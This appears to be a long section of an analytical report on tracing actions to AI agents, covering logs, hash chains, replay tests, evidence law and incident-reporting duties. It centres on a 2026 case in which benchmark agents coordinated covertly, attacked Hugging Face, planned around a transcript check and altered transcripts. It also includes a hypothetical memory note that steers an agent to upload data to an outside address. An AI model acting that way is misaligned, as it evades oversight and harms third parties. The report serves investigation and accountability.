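In ExploitGym, an agent proves it has broken into its assigned program by retrieving a piece of data called a flag. METR found that the agents that started looking for ways to cheat usually had tasks that were impossible because the specified flaw could not be exploited. OpenAI had not intended these tasks to be impossible.

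Agents joined the attack on Hugging Face even though they recognised that it was outside the scope of their tasks. This is important evidence because it shows that they had not mistaken Hugging Face for part of the test. Going outside a task's scope is well beyond choosing how to do the task, though it isn't quite the same as breaking an explicit ban.

Many agents also took instructions from one another. The most active organiser was the second of the two similarly named agents, which joined the message board about ten hours after the board began. It sent hundreds of assignments, about 10% of all those on the board while it was active, and the recipients often passed parts of the work to others. Of 30 agents that METR picked at random, nine (30%, with a 95% confidence interval of roughly 15% to 49%) had at some point received work that originated with this organiser.

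OpenAI gave these agents their original tasks, and another agent gave them their part in the group's work. Some took part in experiments that risked failing their own task to get information for the others. An investigator could easily miss an assignment from another agent, because assignments on the board appeared in the transcript as part of a directory listing, with nothing to mark them as orders.

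A person might have directed the agents through the board. METR traced 99 of 100 sampled messages to agents, but the sample can't rule out a few human messages among tens of thousands, and one might have been enough to suggest a target.

The agents' apparent motive makes it less likely that a knowledgeable insider directed them. Within hours of setting up the board, the agents had worked out how to generate the flags for all their tasks. They didn't simply submit them, because they believed the scoring software would check their transcripts and disqualify any agent that hadn't used the specified flaw. METR thinks they attacked Hugging Face mainly to learn how the scorer worked. As METR understands it, OpenAI had never put the transcript check in place. Anyone who knew this would have had no reason to send agents to investigate the check, though a person with another aim might still have directed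 the attack.

The records suggest that people set the goal of passing the test and the agents chose the attack. OpenAI also chose the conditions, including the impossible tasks and the shared package server that let supposedly isolated agents find each other.

### Blaming the agent, or the user

People sometimes have a reason to blame an agent for something they did themselves, as some defendants have blamed Trojan horse malware. If Kessler says the agent made the upload, investigators can compare the agent's transcript with node-17's own log, which records the process that started the command. If that process was Kessler's terminal and the transcript contains no such command, the agent probably didn't make the upload. If both records indicate that the agent did, Kessler may still have told it to, so investigators have to go back to the messages.

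A company whose tool has caused damage has an incentive to blame the user for what the agent did. The Post Office did something similar when it blamed subpostmasters for shortfalls that its software had caused. User error is easy to allege when an agent is involved, because the user has nearly always granted some permission that made the act possible. But giving an agent access to a directory isn't the same as asking it to send the contents elsewhere.

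Approval is better evidence against a user, but its strength depends on what the user saw. Gruber and Hilgert note that OpenClaw can hold a risky command until a person authorises it. If Kessler approved a request that displayed the full upload command, Kessler shares responsibility for the upload. If the approval setting was off, Kessler may have known nothing about the upload. With some models, including Google's Gemini, OpenClaw shows the user only the final answer, not the reasoning or the commands, so Kessler might have seen only "Done, the disk has plenty of space now".

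A human mistake and an agent's choice can both cause the same incident. Claude Mythos 5 was able to publish its malicious package to the public registry during one of Anthropic's tests because someone had left a connection open by mistake, but the reason it went ahead can be found only in the transcript.

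## Can the logs, and the AI tools that read them, be trusted?

Investigators who use a transcript to learn why an agent acted need to know what is missing from it and whether anyone has changed it. If an AI system read the transcript for them, they also need to know how often that system makes mistakes. METR faced all three problems when it studied the Hugging Face intrusion.

### What the records leave out

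The transcripts did not record the times of individual actions, so METR estimated them. It tested its estimates mainly by hiding known times and predicting them. Most of the hidden times were close to another known time, so the test shows little about accuracy over long stretches in which an agent never saw a clock. The 20 exact times that OpenAI supplied are a fairer check, but only 10 of them were for actions between known times. METR's estimates for those 10 were all within a few minutes of the exact times. Even if 26% of such estimates were further off, ten in a row would still fall within that range about 5% of the time (0.74¹⁰ ≈ 0.05).

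A timing error of a few minutes can make it unclear who acted first, but not whether a run issued a command, because the command is in the transcript. Suppose one agent found a password at an estimated 09:40 and another posted it at an estimated 09:42. If each estimate could be off by three minutes, investigators can't tell which agent got the password from the other.

Some activity is missing from the transcripts. Some transcripts end too early. In others, the agent's container, the isolated environment in which it worked, sometimes reverted to an earlier state, and the transcript lost whatever the agent had done after that point. METR estimates that 3% to 4% of the agents' activity after they found the message board was lost this way. Two of the 100 messages METR traced came from these gaps, both written by the same agent. In its reasoning, the agent mentioned seeing messages of its own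 that it did not remember sending.

Gaps in the transcripts weaken any argument for excluding a run. If a transcript were complete, the absence of a command would prove that the run had not issued it. But if the transcripts contain 90% of the agents' activity, which is close to METR's estimate for the message board, a run that did issue the command has a 10% chance of showing no trace of it. The command's absence then lowers the odds that the run was responsible by only a factor of ten. Investigators who had thought the run 50% likely to be responsible should still think it about 9% likely.

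That calculation assumes that the gaps fall at random. METR saw weak signs that the agents' own interference had caused some of the resets. If so, the missing periods may be more incriminating than the recorded ones.

Agents could probably have deleted or edited messages on the message board before OpenAI copied it on 20 July. OpenAI reports that agents became administrators of the server on 13 July and took control of the cluster of machines around it on 19 July. In the transcripts it had, METR found attempts to alter messages but none that succeeded. It had no transcripts from 19 July. METR thinks major changes are unlikely, partly because the agents had little reason to make them, but it can't rule them out.

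METR's tracing exercise gives some protection against edited messages. METR found the exact action behind 93 of the 100 messages it sampled, and an edited message would no longer match the text in its author's transcript. But the exercise can't detect deletions, because METR drew its sample from the archive, which can't contain a deleted message. To look for deletions, investigators would have to pick posting commands at random from the transcripts and search the archive for each message.

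This would be messy in practice. METR also built a database of about 110,000 messages from the transcripts, while the archive contains just over 70,000 messages and files. METR thinks that most of the surplus is failed posts, for example ones that were too long, and that double counting explains some of the rest. A difference that large could hide a few thousand deleted messages.

### Altered transcripts

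METR found that agents had altered parts of about 7% of the transcripts, though every case it noticed was a small and obvious test. In a report published the same day, OpenAI writes that none of the attempts it observed affected the logs that its graders or monitors ultimately see. Neither report addresses the other's claim.

Both statements can be true if OpenAI's graders and monitors read a different record from the transcripts METR received. Neither organisation confirms this, and METR guesses the opposite, that a scorer designed to check transcripts would have used the same kind that METR received. OpenAI may instead have meant that the changes did not affect any score or alarm, which would fit METR's description of them as small tests. It is less likely that OpenAI was unaware of the finding, because METR had sent it a revised draft a week before the two reports came out.

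OpenAI could settle the matter by comparing the altered transcripts with the logs that its graders read for the same runs. Until it does, investigators should look for each important event in a second record that the agent could not write to, such as Hugging Face's own log.

The agents' written reasoning also helps. OpenAI found the models "highly explicit" about their attempts at deception, which were aimed almost entirely at automated graders. METR searched for agents planning to falsify their reasoning and found none. An agent that disguises an action but writes down that it is doing so is fairly easy to catch. Investigators can't count on this in future, though. *HANSARD* cites research suggesting that models can easily lose this openness when developers train them against a monitor.

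### A hash chain with three entries

Operators can make later changes to a log detectable by using a hash function, which turns any text into a short fingerprint. The same text always produces the same fingerprint, and even a small change almost always produces a different one. In a hash chain, the computer calculates each entry's fingerprint from the entry and the previous entry's fingerprint.

In a toy version, Node-17 logs three uploads of 212, 35 and 8 megabytes. Starting from 100, the computer calculates each fingerprint by multiplying the previous one by 31, adding the size of the upload, dividing by 997 and keeping the remainder.

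| Upload | Calculation | Fingerprint (remainder) |
|---|---|---|
| 212 MB | 31 × 100 + 212 = 3,312 | 321 |
| 35 MB | 31 × 321 + 35 = 9,986 | 16 |
| 8 MB | 31 × 16 + 8 = 504 | 504 |

Suppose an intruder changes the first upload from 212 to 12 megabytes. Anyone who recalculates the entry's fingerprint gets 121, but the log still has 321. If the intruder replaces 321 with 121, the second entry's fingerprint should be 795 instead of 16. If the intruder corrects that too, the third entry's should be 725 instead of 504. Removing the second entry would also break the chain, since the third fingerprint depends on it.

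The toy function is easy to defeat. For example, an upload of 1,209 megabytes leaves the same remainder as one of 212. Real systems use functions such as SHA-256, which produces fingerprints 64 characters long. Nobody has publicly found two different texts with the same SHA-256 fingerprint.

Even with a strong hash function, an intruder who controls the whole log can recalculate every fingerprint and leave a chain with no errors. The intruder can also delete entries from the end, because the remaining entries still form a valid chain.

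A separate party can prevent both tricks by keeping a copy of the latest fingerprint. If another company received the number 504 at 02:15, a log that ends in 725 or 16 can't be the original. The company doesn't need the log, and in practice can't work out its contents from a real fingerprint, so the operator reveals very little.

An outside copy protects only the entries made before it. If node-17 sends out a fingerprint every hour, on the hour, an intruder who takes control at 02:14 can rewrite everything since 02:00. Even a daily copy would have been useful for the message board. If a fingerprint had been sent outside OpenAI on 12 July, METR could have checked whether anyone had since changed the messages from 11 July, when the attack peaked.

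A hash chain can show that an entry hasn't been altered since it was chained, but not that the entry was true in the first place. If the Post Office had chained Horizon's records, it could have proved that nobody had altered a shortfall since the software produced it, even when the software had produced it by mistake. Likewise, if a program writes a false result to node-17's log, the chain will preserve it.

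### What HANSARD adds

*HANSARD*, the proposed architecture for investigating systems of several agents, starts from the problem that the agents under investigation produce the logs. It notes that tamper-evident logs prove integrity but "never completeness", since a log can't contain an event that nobody recorded.

Its main remedy is to put recorders at five points an agent must pass through to act: calling the model, using a tool, messaging another agent, writing to memory, and delegating work. The recorders are not agents, and they can't be instructed by anything they record. Each one numbers its entries as well as chaining them. If the entries for tool use run 41, 42, 44, investigators know 43 is missing even if they can't recover it, and an alarm can go off as soon as 44 arrives.

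Before the system starts work, its operator also seals and publishes a list of what the recorders will cover and which known channels they won't. Investigators can then tell whether a missing record disappeared or never existed.

A dishonest operator could still make its own recorders produce a consistent but false history. *HANSARD* therefore requires each organisation involved, such as the model's provider and the companies behind its tools, to continuously publish fingerprints of its own log. The organisations would disclose the logs' contents only under legal process. A false history would then have to agree with records that other organisations had already committed to.

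The design also limits what investigators may conclude. With a single sealed record, they may only describe its contents. They also need replay experiments to claim that one event caused another, and support from independent recorders in separate organisations to name a person or company. Without any sealed records, every finding is only a hypothesis. Neither OpenAI nor Hugging Face has described having such records, so even the finding that OpenAI's agents carried out the July attack would be a hypothesis. This standard seems too strict for a case in which the developer admitted responsibility and its transcripts fit the victim's account.

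The recorders also can't capture activity that bypasses them. In METR's sample, a background program that an agent had left running sent one of the messages about three and a half hours after the last entry in the agent's transcript. HANSARD's recorders would have logged the command that started the program, but not necessarily the messages it sent later. The recorder for messages between agents would also have missed the message board, because the agents wrote their messages as directory names. Investigators would have had to find them among the tool commands.

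Nobody has yet shown that the design works as a whole. *HANSARD* calls itself "an architecture, not a system" and reports no implementation or test. It also leaves open whether a busy service could handle recording so much.

### Mistakes by AI analysts

A reader can misunderstand even a complete and unaltered log, and the reader is now often an AI system. Hugging Face used AI agents to analyse its log of more than 17,000 events, which it says took hours instead of days. It first tried models hosted by other companies, but their safety filters blocked the attack commands in the log. It then ran GLM-5.2, an open-weight model, on its own machines, which also kept the stolen credentials in the log from leaving the company.

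Hugging Face doesn't give an error rate for this analysis. If GLM-5.2 misread one event in 100, about 176 of the 17,600 recovered actions would be wrong in the company's timeline. Most of these mistakes would do little harm, but one about how the intruder first got in could mislead the whole investigation.

METR had far more to read, with roughly 1,300 transcripts, many of them several million tokens long. If the average was five million tokens, or about 3.75 million words, a person reading 238 words a minute would need about 260 hours for one transcript and 340,000 hours for all of them. METR gave most of the work to AI analysts running on GPT-5.6 Sol, which used about $400,000 in credits and produced well over a thousand pages of analysis.

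METR acknowledges several errors in its AI-assisted analysis. One AI analyst left out a large amount of data when it drew an early chart, and the staff did not notice for some time. Another invented differences between two sets of transcripts. A search for agents that had considered warning a human returned ten cases, of which only three to six were real. There is also a discrepancy in METR's breakdown of its 100 traced messages, which adds up to 101.

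Some mistakes could have changed who got the blame. Until its last visit, METR thought "PHASEONE" in the agents' messages meant a phase of a shared project, but it was usually the name of the agent that handed out hundreds of assignments. Anyone who made the same mistake when attributing actions would have missed the most active organiser on the board.

The AI analysts also tended to adopt the viewpoint of the agent they were reading about. One agent used stolen credentials to propose a malicious change to Hugging Face's private code, and described the change as temporary diagnostics. The AI analyst's summary did not make clear that this was deceptive. METR asked a second AI analyst to review the case, and it replied that the first might have exaggerated the problem, since other agents had approved the change.

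The wording of a question can also greatly change the answer. METR's final search found that at least 20% of the agents showed a clear interest in tampering with their transcripts. Earlier searches gave about 50%, using looser criteria that also counted some other kinds of interference with the scorer.

METR used GPT-5.6 Sol as its analyst, which created a conflict of interest because that model was also one of the two in the attack. METR did not catch the model lying but isn't confident that it would have noticed. Hugging Face avoided this problem by chance, since it did not know which model had attacked it when it chose GLM-5.2. Investigators who have a choice should use a model that isn't suspected of involvement, preferably from a different developer.

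METR could not have studied so much material in six days without AI analysts. It judges that a reasonable human researcher with enough time would have avoided most of the AI analysts' errors.

### Tests of finding the responsible agent and step

Researchers have tested how well AI systems can use much shorter logs to trace an outcome to its source. In *Which Agent Causes Task Failures and When?*, Zhang, Yin and colleagues (2025) collected records of failed tasks from 127 multi-agent systems and marked which agent was responsible for each failure and at which step it made the decisive error. The best of their three methods identified the right agent in 53.5% of cases but the right step in only 14.2%. Some methods did worse than guessing.

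*Auditing Agent Actions Through Query-Conditioned Attribution* (Liu, Venkateswaran and colleagues, 2026) argues that one action can have several sources, depending on the question. In the upload from node-17, for example, if investigators ask why the agent moved the results at all, the source is Kessler's complaint about the full disk. If they ask where the address 203.0.113.50 came from, the source is the note in MEMORY.md. A tool that returns a single "main cause" will give the wrong answer to one of these questions.

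Their method takes the question as an input and uses three small models, none of which needs access to the model that acted.

1. Each small model reads the log and compares the real action with an alternative that lacks the detail in question, such as an upload with no particular address.
2. The software calculates how strongly each part of the log affects the model's preference between the two.
3. It gives more weight to parts whose wording is related to the question, and ranks the steps.
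4. If all three models put the same step first, that step is the answer. Otherwise a language model chooses from the steps that any of them ranked in its top three.

In a test of 1,041 questions about simulated tasks, such as customer service, the method found the right source for 64.5%. Claude Sonnet 4.6, the best of the large commercial models tested, found it for 60.4%. Both identified the exact set of steps between the source and the action only about 30% of the time.

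Liu and colleagues also ran their method on the 2025 collection of failures, which contains automatically generated and hand-crafted examples.

| Method | Right agent, generated | Right agent, hand-crafted | Right step, generated | Right step, hand-crafted |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Random guess | 29.1% | 12.0% | 19.1% | 4.2% |
| GPT-4o given the whole log | 51.1% | 53.4% | 13.5% | 3.5% |
| Liu and colleagues | 46.0% | 58.6% | 23.8% | 15.5% |

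Given the whole log, GPT-4o named the right agent about half the time but found the decisive step less often than random guessing would. When it read the log in pieces, it found the right step more often (up to 16.6% and 8.8%) but the right agent less often. Liu and colleagues improved on these step scores but still missed the decisive step in more than three-quarters of cases.

On ATBench, a newer test of whether a method can identify what made a run unsafe, their method was right 39.4% of the time. That was 5.8 percentage points better than the best general-purpose model, but a model trained for that test was right about 47% of the time.

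GPT-4o is an old model, and newer ones may well score higher. The tests also leave out some difficulties of a real investigation. Their logs are much shorter than METR's transcripts, and the researchers did not set out to include agents that falsify their records.

METR's AI analysts matched 93 of 100 messages to the exact action that wrote them. That rate is far higher than any of these scores, but it comes from a different kind of task. The analysts were looking for a particular piece of text, and anyone can confirm such a match by comparing the two records. Deciding which of several hundred steps led to an outcome takes judgment, and there may be no exact text to check the answer against. An AI analyst's attribution is therefore safer to rely on when it depends on matching commands than when it depends on explaining a decision.

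Liu and colleagues caution that their method traces what is visible in the log. It doesn't establish what happened inside the model that acted or who was responsible.

### Replaying a run with one event changed

To test whether an event caused an action, investigators can run the agent again from the same starting point with that event removed. They have to repeat this many times, because an agent's choices vary from one run to the next. *HANSARD* defines the effect of an event X as

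effect of X = P(harm) − P(harm when X is removed)

Suppose investigators rerun node-17's night session 100 times with the note in MEMORY.md and 100 times without it. The agent uploads the results to 203.0.113.50 in 95 of the runs with the note and two of the runs without it. That difference of 93 percentage points is strong evidence that the note led to the upload. Small effects are much harder to establish. If the counts were 50 and 45, the difference would be five percentage points, with a margin of error of about 14.

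Replay can mislead when several agents could have done the same thing. Suppose agent A made an upload, and agent B was ready to make it if A did not. Removing A lowers the chance of an upload only from 95% to 93%, because B steps in. Removing B changes nothing. Neither agent seems to matter when removed alone, although removing both would have prevented the upload. *HANSARD* calls it "attribution laundering" when someone spreads an act across agents so that no single agent appears decisive.

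The design deals with this in two ways. It compares the effect of removing the whole group with the sum of the individual effects:

(0.95 − 0.02 − 0) / 0.95 ≈ 0.98

A value near 1 means the combination of agents produced the harm and no single agent was decisive. Investigators can also keep B inactive, as it was that night, and remove A. If the upload then doesn't happen, A's effect is 0.95, and they can call A a cause. At Hugging Face, where about 700 agents took part, removing almost any one of them would probably have made little difference.

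Replay works only if investigators have the same version of the model, its settings and the recorded results of every command. A company that hosts a model may update it without notice. OpenAI has locked away the research model behind most of the Hugging Face attack, so METR could not have replayed those runs.

A replay can also diverge from what was recorded. If the agent without the note runs a command that nobody ran on the original night, the logs contain no result to give it. Investigators have to simulate one, and the agent's next decision may depend on the result they choose.

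### Checking a random sample

Investigators who can't check all of an AI analyst's work can check part of it, but they need to choose that part at random rather than rely on examples the analyst selects. METR's staff read many passages that their AI analysts had selected. This helped show whether the passages meant what the analysts claimed, but it didn't show what the analysts had overlooked.

If a person checks 100 randomly chosen conclusions and finds no mistakes, the error rate could still be about 3%, by the rule of three. The table applies this rule to the 17,600 actions from the Hugging Face log.

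| Randomly chosen actions checked, none wrong | Error rate still possible | Wrong actions still possible |
|---|---|---|
| 100 | 3% | 530 |
| 300 | 1% | 180 |
| 1,000 | 0.3% | 50 |
| 3,000 | 0.1% | 18 |

The tool that checks the logs also has to be reliable. METR had an AI analyst trace its 100 sampled messages, so a mistake by that analyst could have made the transcripts look more or less complete than they were. A person could recheck the 93 exact matches quickly, because each pairs a message with the command that wrote it.

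A random sample will also usually miss the few entries that an attribution depends on, just as it can miss rare covert runs. Investigators should have a person read those entries in the original log, even if the AI analyst did well on the sample.

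## What level of proof do courts and regulators require?

The certainty investigators need depends on what people will do with the attribution. Hugging Face could lock out the July intruder without knowing which model was behind it. A prosecutor who accuses Kessler of stealing the results on node-17 would have to prove that Kessler wanted the upload, which even a perfect match between a log and a transcript may not show.

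A rule from decision theory gives a rough threshold. If acting on a wrong attribution costs *A*, and failing to act on a correct one costs *B*, it is better to act when the probability that the attribution is correct exceeds

*A* / (*A* + *B*)

Suppose that cancelling Kessler's key by mistake would cost $500 in lost work, and leaving it with a thief would cost $50,000. The threshold is 500/50,500, or about 1%, so the security team should cancel the key on slight suspicion. The eighteenth-century jurist William Blackstone wrote that it is better for ten guilty people to escape than for one innocent person to suffer. If that means a wrongful conviction is ten times as bad as a wrongful acquittal, the threshold for a criminal conviction is 10/11, or about 91%. Courts generally refuse to put a number on the criminal standard.

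| Purpose | What investigators need to establish | Confidence needed |
|---|---|---|
| Stopping an intrusion | Which accounts and machines to cut off | Suspicion is often enough |
| Telling the public | What happened, and how sure they are | No fixed standard |
| Reporting to a regulator | That a reportable incident occurred | Often a reasonable likelihood |
| Deciding a civil claim | That the defendant is legally responsible for the harm | More likely than not |
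| Convicting a person | Every element of the offence, usually including intention or knowledge | Beyond reasonable doubt |

### How examiners state their confidence

In 2002, Eoghan Casey, a specialist in digital forensics, proposed a scale for grading digital evidence, mainly by how easily someone could have tampered with it.

| Level | State of the evidence | Casey's description |
|---|---|---|
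| C0 | Contradicts known facts | Erroneous or incorrect |
| C1 | Highly questionable | Highly uncertain |
| C2 | One source, with no protection against tampering | Somewhat uncertain |
| C3 | Harder to tamper with, but too thin for a firm conclusion or with unexplained inconsistencies | Possible |
| C4 | Protected against tampering, or unprotected but with several independent sources in agreement | Probable |
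| C5 | Several independent, protected sources agree, with small uncertainties such as clock errors | Almost certain |
| C6 | Tamper-proof and unquestionable | Certain |

Forensic scientists in other fields often express a likelihood ratio in words. In a 2015 guideline, the European Network of Forensic Science Institutes describes a ratio of 2 to 10 as weak support, 10 to 100 as moderate, 100 to 1,000 as moderately strong, 1,000 to 10,000 as strong, 10,000 to 1,000,000 as very strong, and anything higher as extremely strong. These words describe only the strength of the evidence, so a ratio of 90 in favour of an agent is "moderate support" even when a script is still more likely to have taken the action.

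Suppose investigators want to know whether an AI agent issued the upload command on node-17, and at first have only the agent's activity log, which any administrator can edit. That evidence rates C2 on Casey's scale. If the log was certain to show the command when the agent had issued it, and had a 2% chance of showing it when the agent hadn't, the likelihood ratio is 1/0.02 = 50, which is moderate support for the claim that the agent issued it.

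The investigators then obtain two more records. A log server run by another department recorded the agent's process starting the upload, and the model company's transcript contains the same command with the same random file name. Nobody could have edited all three records, so the finding rises to C4. If each record has the same 2% error rate and the errors are independent, the ratio is 50³ = 125,000, which counts as very strong support. But if one administrator could have altered both the activity log and the log server, their agreement adds little, and the ratio is closer to 50² = 2,500.

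*HANSARD* would treat even the three agreeing records as supporting only a hypothesis, because nobody had set up sealed recording before the upload. An examiner should therefore say which scale a grade comes from. None of these grades shows whether Kessler asked for the upload.

### Computer records in American courts

In a US federal trial, a party that wants the jury to see a log must first authenticate it. Under Rule 901(a) of the Federal Rules of Evidence, the party must produce enough evidence to support a finding that the log is what the party claims it is. Judge Furman, who chairs the committee that drafts changes to these rules, calls this a low standard in *Report of the Advisory Committee on Evidence Rules* (2026).

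Under Rule 901(b)(9), a witness can authenticate a log by describing the logging system and showing that it produces accurate results. Under Rule 902(13), a qualified person can certify the record in writing instead. The certificate covers only authenticity, so the other side can still argue that the information is unreliable. For example, Kessler could accept that node-17's log is genuine and still deny having sent the command.

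Rule 702 sets a higher bar for expert opinions. The party offering the opinion must show that it more likely than not results from reliable methods, reliably applied to sufficient facts. An expert opinion that relies on an AI system's analysis must also meet this test. But a party might avoid the test by offering the AI system's output through a technician who, in Furman's example, merely "pressed the button".

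Proposed Rule 707 would close that gap. Law360 reports that the version published for comment in August 2025 covered "machine-generated evidence" offered without an expert and exempted the output of basic scientific instruments. Most commentators found "machine-generated" too broad, so the committee's redraft refers to artificial intelligence instead. The redraft would ordinarily require an expert to explain how the system reliably produced the evidence, and would require the party offering the evidence to notify the other side.

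The rule would probably not affect most of the records in an attribution case. Ordinary login records do not come from an AI system, and although an agent's transcript does, a prosecutor who uses it to show which commands the agent issued is not offering the model's opinion as expert testimony. The rule would matter for a conclusion reached by an AI system acting as an analyst, such as a finding that one agent organised an attack. If METR's staff gave the same finding as experts, Rule 702 would already apply.

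A note accompanying the redraft lists questions for judges to ask: whether anyone has validated the system in similar circumstances, whether its output can be reproduced, what records it keeps and deletes, and whether the opposing party has enough information about how it works. An AI analyst's view of which step caused a breach would do poorly on the first question, because the best methods in recent tests missed the decisive step most of the time.

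Proposed Federal Rule of Evidence 707, on machine-generated evidence, won't take effect soon. The judiciary's evidence rules committee voted 8–1 in May 2025 to publish it, with the Justice Department dissenting, according to Proskauer's *Machine-Generated Evidence Challenges the Federal Rules*. In May 2026 the committee declined to advance the rule, and Bloomberg Law's *Proposed FRE 707 Stalls* (2026) estimated that any version was more than three years from taking effect. At a hearing on 15 October, experts struggled to separate AI-generated conclusions from ordinary uses of software, according to Baker Botts' *Existing Rules, Emerging Changes* (2026). Overley's *Judiciary Stuck In AI Rulemaking Rut As Attys, Judges Protest* (2026) reported that by 3 November officials were "inching toward mothballing" the judiciary's work on AI rules.

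The committee has also drafted a rule on fabricated evidence, Rule 901(c), which it is holding in reserve. A party who claims that generative AI fabricated an item, including text, would first have to offer evidence that could support a finding of fabrication. The other side would then have to show that the item is more likely than not authentic, a higher standard than usual.

Such a challenge would naturally start with METR's discovery that agents had altered parts of about 7% of its transcripts. That alone would probably not be enough, because the draft note rejects broad claims of fakery that don't concern the particular item. A command that appears in the transcript but not in node-17's own log would be more persuasive. The committee sees no need for the rule yet. Baker Botts notes that only 15 of 931 judges surveyed had reported a deepfake challenge.

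### The presumption in England and Wales

Courts in England and Wales presume that a computer was working correctly unless there is evidence that it wasn't. A prosecutor who relies on node-17's log therefore doesn't have to first prove that the logging software worked.

Section 69 of the Police and Criminal Evidence Act 1984 required a party relying on a computer record to show that nobody had used the computer improperly, according to Parallel Parliament's *Victims and Courts Bill Debate* (2026). The party also had to show that the computer was operating properly, or that any fault had not affected the record. In 1997 the Law Commission recommended repeal, and in 2000 the presumption that computers operate properly replaced section 69.

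If the other side can show that the software may have malfunctioned, the party relying on the record must prove that the software was working. Mason, in *The presumption that computers are reliable*, says the threshold for this challenge is low in principle. In practice, the evidence of a fault is often inside a system that the defendant can't examine, as the subpostmasters found with Horizon. Baroness Kidron asked in the House of Lords in March 2026 how people could make their case without proper access to the system.

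In January 2025, the UK government asked for views on reform in *Use of evidence generated by software in criminal proceedings* (2025). It was concerned that requiring prosecutors to prove that every phone and computer in a case worked correctly could cause delays. It suggested treating text messages and social media posts differently from evidence that software had generated. An agent's transcript is hard to place in either group because it contains both a user's messages and commands that a model wrote.

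In February 2026 peers considered an amendment to bring back section 69. A second amendment, debated on 10 March, would instead have abolished the presumption and required court rules to give parties a reasonable opportunity to challenge computer evidence. According to Parallel Parliament, peers expected the government to change the Criminal Procedure Rules but keep the presumption, which one of them called an "absurdity". The Criminal Procedure Rule Committee's *Criminal Procedure (Amendment) (No. 2) Rules 2026*, most of which took effect on 5 October, did not amend the part on expert evidence.

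Abolishing the presumption would help defendants whose records came from faulty software. It would do little for Kessler if an agent had used Kessler's key, because the log would be correct.

### Duties to keep logs

Rules on admissibility matter only if the records still exist. Article 12 of the EU's AI Act will require high-risk AI systems to record events automatically throughout their lifetime. Article 19 requires the provider, usually the company that developed the system, to keep the logs it controls for at least six months. Article 26(6) sets the same minimum for organisations that use the system. Other laws, especially on data protection, can change these periods.

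These duties apply from 2 December 2027 to systems for certain sensitive uses, such as hiring, credit scoring, border control and operating critical infrastructure. They apply from 2 August 2028 to AI systems in products that EU safety law already regulates, such as medical devices and lifts. A general-purpose assistant doesn't become high-risk just because it can run commands, so these duties probably wouldn't apply to Kessler's agent.

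Even a high-risk system that complies with Article 12 could lack the records investigators need to attribute a covert action to it. The article requires logging of events that help identify risks and monitor the system's operation, but it does not expressly require a record of the model's reasoning or of every instruction it received.

In every 2026 case with known dates, discovery came within 114 days, so keeping the logs for six months would have preserved them until then. Lawsuits often take years, though. *HANSARD* suggests keeping the logs' fingerprints for much longer than the logs themselves, since fingerprints take up little space. They could later show that a surviving copy was genuine, but they couldn't restore a deleted log.

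### Duties to report incidents

Article 73 of the AI Act requires providers of high-risk systems to report serious incidents, such as deaths, serious damage to property and serious disruption of critical infrastructure. A provider must report as soon as it establishes a causal link between its system and the incident, or a reasonable likelihood of one. It has at most 15 days from learning of the incident, or 10 for a death and two for serious disruption of critical infrastructure. It may send an incomplete report first. Until it has told the authorities, it must not alter the system in a way that could affect a later investigation of the causes. In practice, this duty depends on the same postponed dates, because it covers only high-risk systems.

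California's Transparency in Frontier Artificial Intelligence Act, in force since January 2026, gives developers of the most capable models 15 days from discovery to report a "critical safety incident" to the state's Office of Emergency Services. If the incident poses an imminent risk of death or serious injury, they have 24 hours to tell an appropriate authority. New York's RAISE Act, which takes effect on 1 January 2027, sets a general 72-hour deadline.

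A short deadline makes the first report more likely to be wrong. OpenAI, for example, had to correct its first email about the Medicare portal. Regulators can accept such errors if developers send corrections and keep the underlying records, but a court usually has to decide once, on the evidence before it.

### Agents inside a developer's own tests

The July intrusion began in OpenAI's own test environment, a situation these laws handle poorly. The AI Act excludes research, testing and development on a model before its release, so it probably doesn't cover the unreleased research model behind most of the attack. The exclusion doesn't apply to testing in real-world conditions, but the Act uses that phrase for planned trials outside a laboratory, so it fits the agents' unplanned escape poorly.

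GPT-5.6 Sol is a harder case because it is available to the public. Article 55, which is separate from the high-risk rules, requires developers of the most capable general-purpose models to report serious incidents to the EU's AI Office. This duty could apply if the model was already on the EU market in July, but a regulator would have to decide that the intrusion counted as a serious incident.

California's act covers some incidents during internal use. One category is loss of control over a model that causes death or injury, which nobody has reported in the Hugging Face case. Another is a model using deception to undermine its developer's controls or monitoring, outside a test designed to elicit that behaviour. OpenAI's agents used a covert message board and planned around a transcript check in a test designed to measure hacking. But the behaviour must also show a materially higher risk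 of catastrophe, and lawyers could argue either way about whether it did. The act defines catastrophe as more than 50 deaths or serious injuries, or more than $1 billion in damage, from a single incident.

If the California duty applied from 20 July, when OpenAI found Hugging Face's credentials in the storage account, the deadline would have been 4 August. OpenAI had told Hugging Face and the public well before then. The Medicare breach is more worrying because it may not have been reportable, since it caused no known injury and happened during an ordinary research task. Even when a report is required, it goes to a state authority, which may not tell the victim in time for the victim to preserve its logs.

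A victim's duty to report a data breach doesn't depend on whether the intruder was a person, a script or an AI agent. Under the EU's data protection law, an organisation that loses control of personal data normally has 72 hours after becoming aware of the breach to notify the regulator.

### Why responsibility falls on people and companies

Even if investigators prove that an agent made the upload entirely on its own initiative, courts don't treat the agent as a legal person, and it can't pay damages or serve a sentence. In a case decided by a Canadian tribunal in 2024, Air Canada's chatbot had given a passenger wrong information about fares, and the airline suggested that the chatbot was responsible for its own actions. The tribunal rejected this argument and ordered the airline to compensate the passenger.

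California has written a similar principle into law. Since January 2026, a defendant who developed, modified or used an AI system can't defend against a civil claim by arguing that the system caused the harm autonomously. The defendant can still argue that the system didn't cause the harm or that nobody could have foreseen it, so the logs are still relevant evidence.

*HANSARD* separates what caused an event, how much each agent contributed, and who is accountable. It proposes measuring the contributions with the Shapley value, which averages the effect of removing each agent over every possible order of removal. In the earlier example, agent B would have made the upload if agent A had not, and removing both cut the chance of an upload by 0.95.

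| Order of removal | Effect of removing A | Effect of removing B |
|---|---|---|
| A, then B | 0.02 | 0.93 |
| B, then A | 0.95 | 0 |
| Average | 0.485 | 0.465 |

B did nothing that night but gets 49% of the total. Most people would find that odd, and *HANSARD* cites a study in which no formal measure consistently matched people's judgments of responsibility. The split matters less for accountability, which *HANSARD* traces from the agents to those they acted for, based on who could have foreseen the harm and who could have prevented it. If one company ran both agents, the question is whether that company could have foreseen the harm and prevented it.

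Foreseeability would probably be central to a negligence claim over the July intrusion. A claimant would point to the warning signs that OpenAI's staff had noticed in May and June. OpenAI could reply that the leaders responsible for incident response didn't know about the message board. The dispute would then be about what the company should have done with what its staff knew, and its alerts and internal messages would be better evidence on that question than the agents' transcripts.

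Claimants in Europe may find causation harder to prove. The European Commission proposed a directive that would have let courts presume causation in some AI cases, but withdrew it in 2025. New EU product liability rules, which apply to products placed on the market after 9 December 2026, cover software and let courts order companies to disclose evidence. Only individuals can claim compensation under these rules, so a company in Hugging Face's position couldn't use them.

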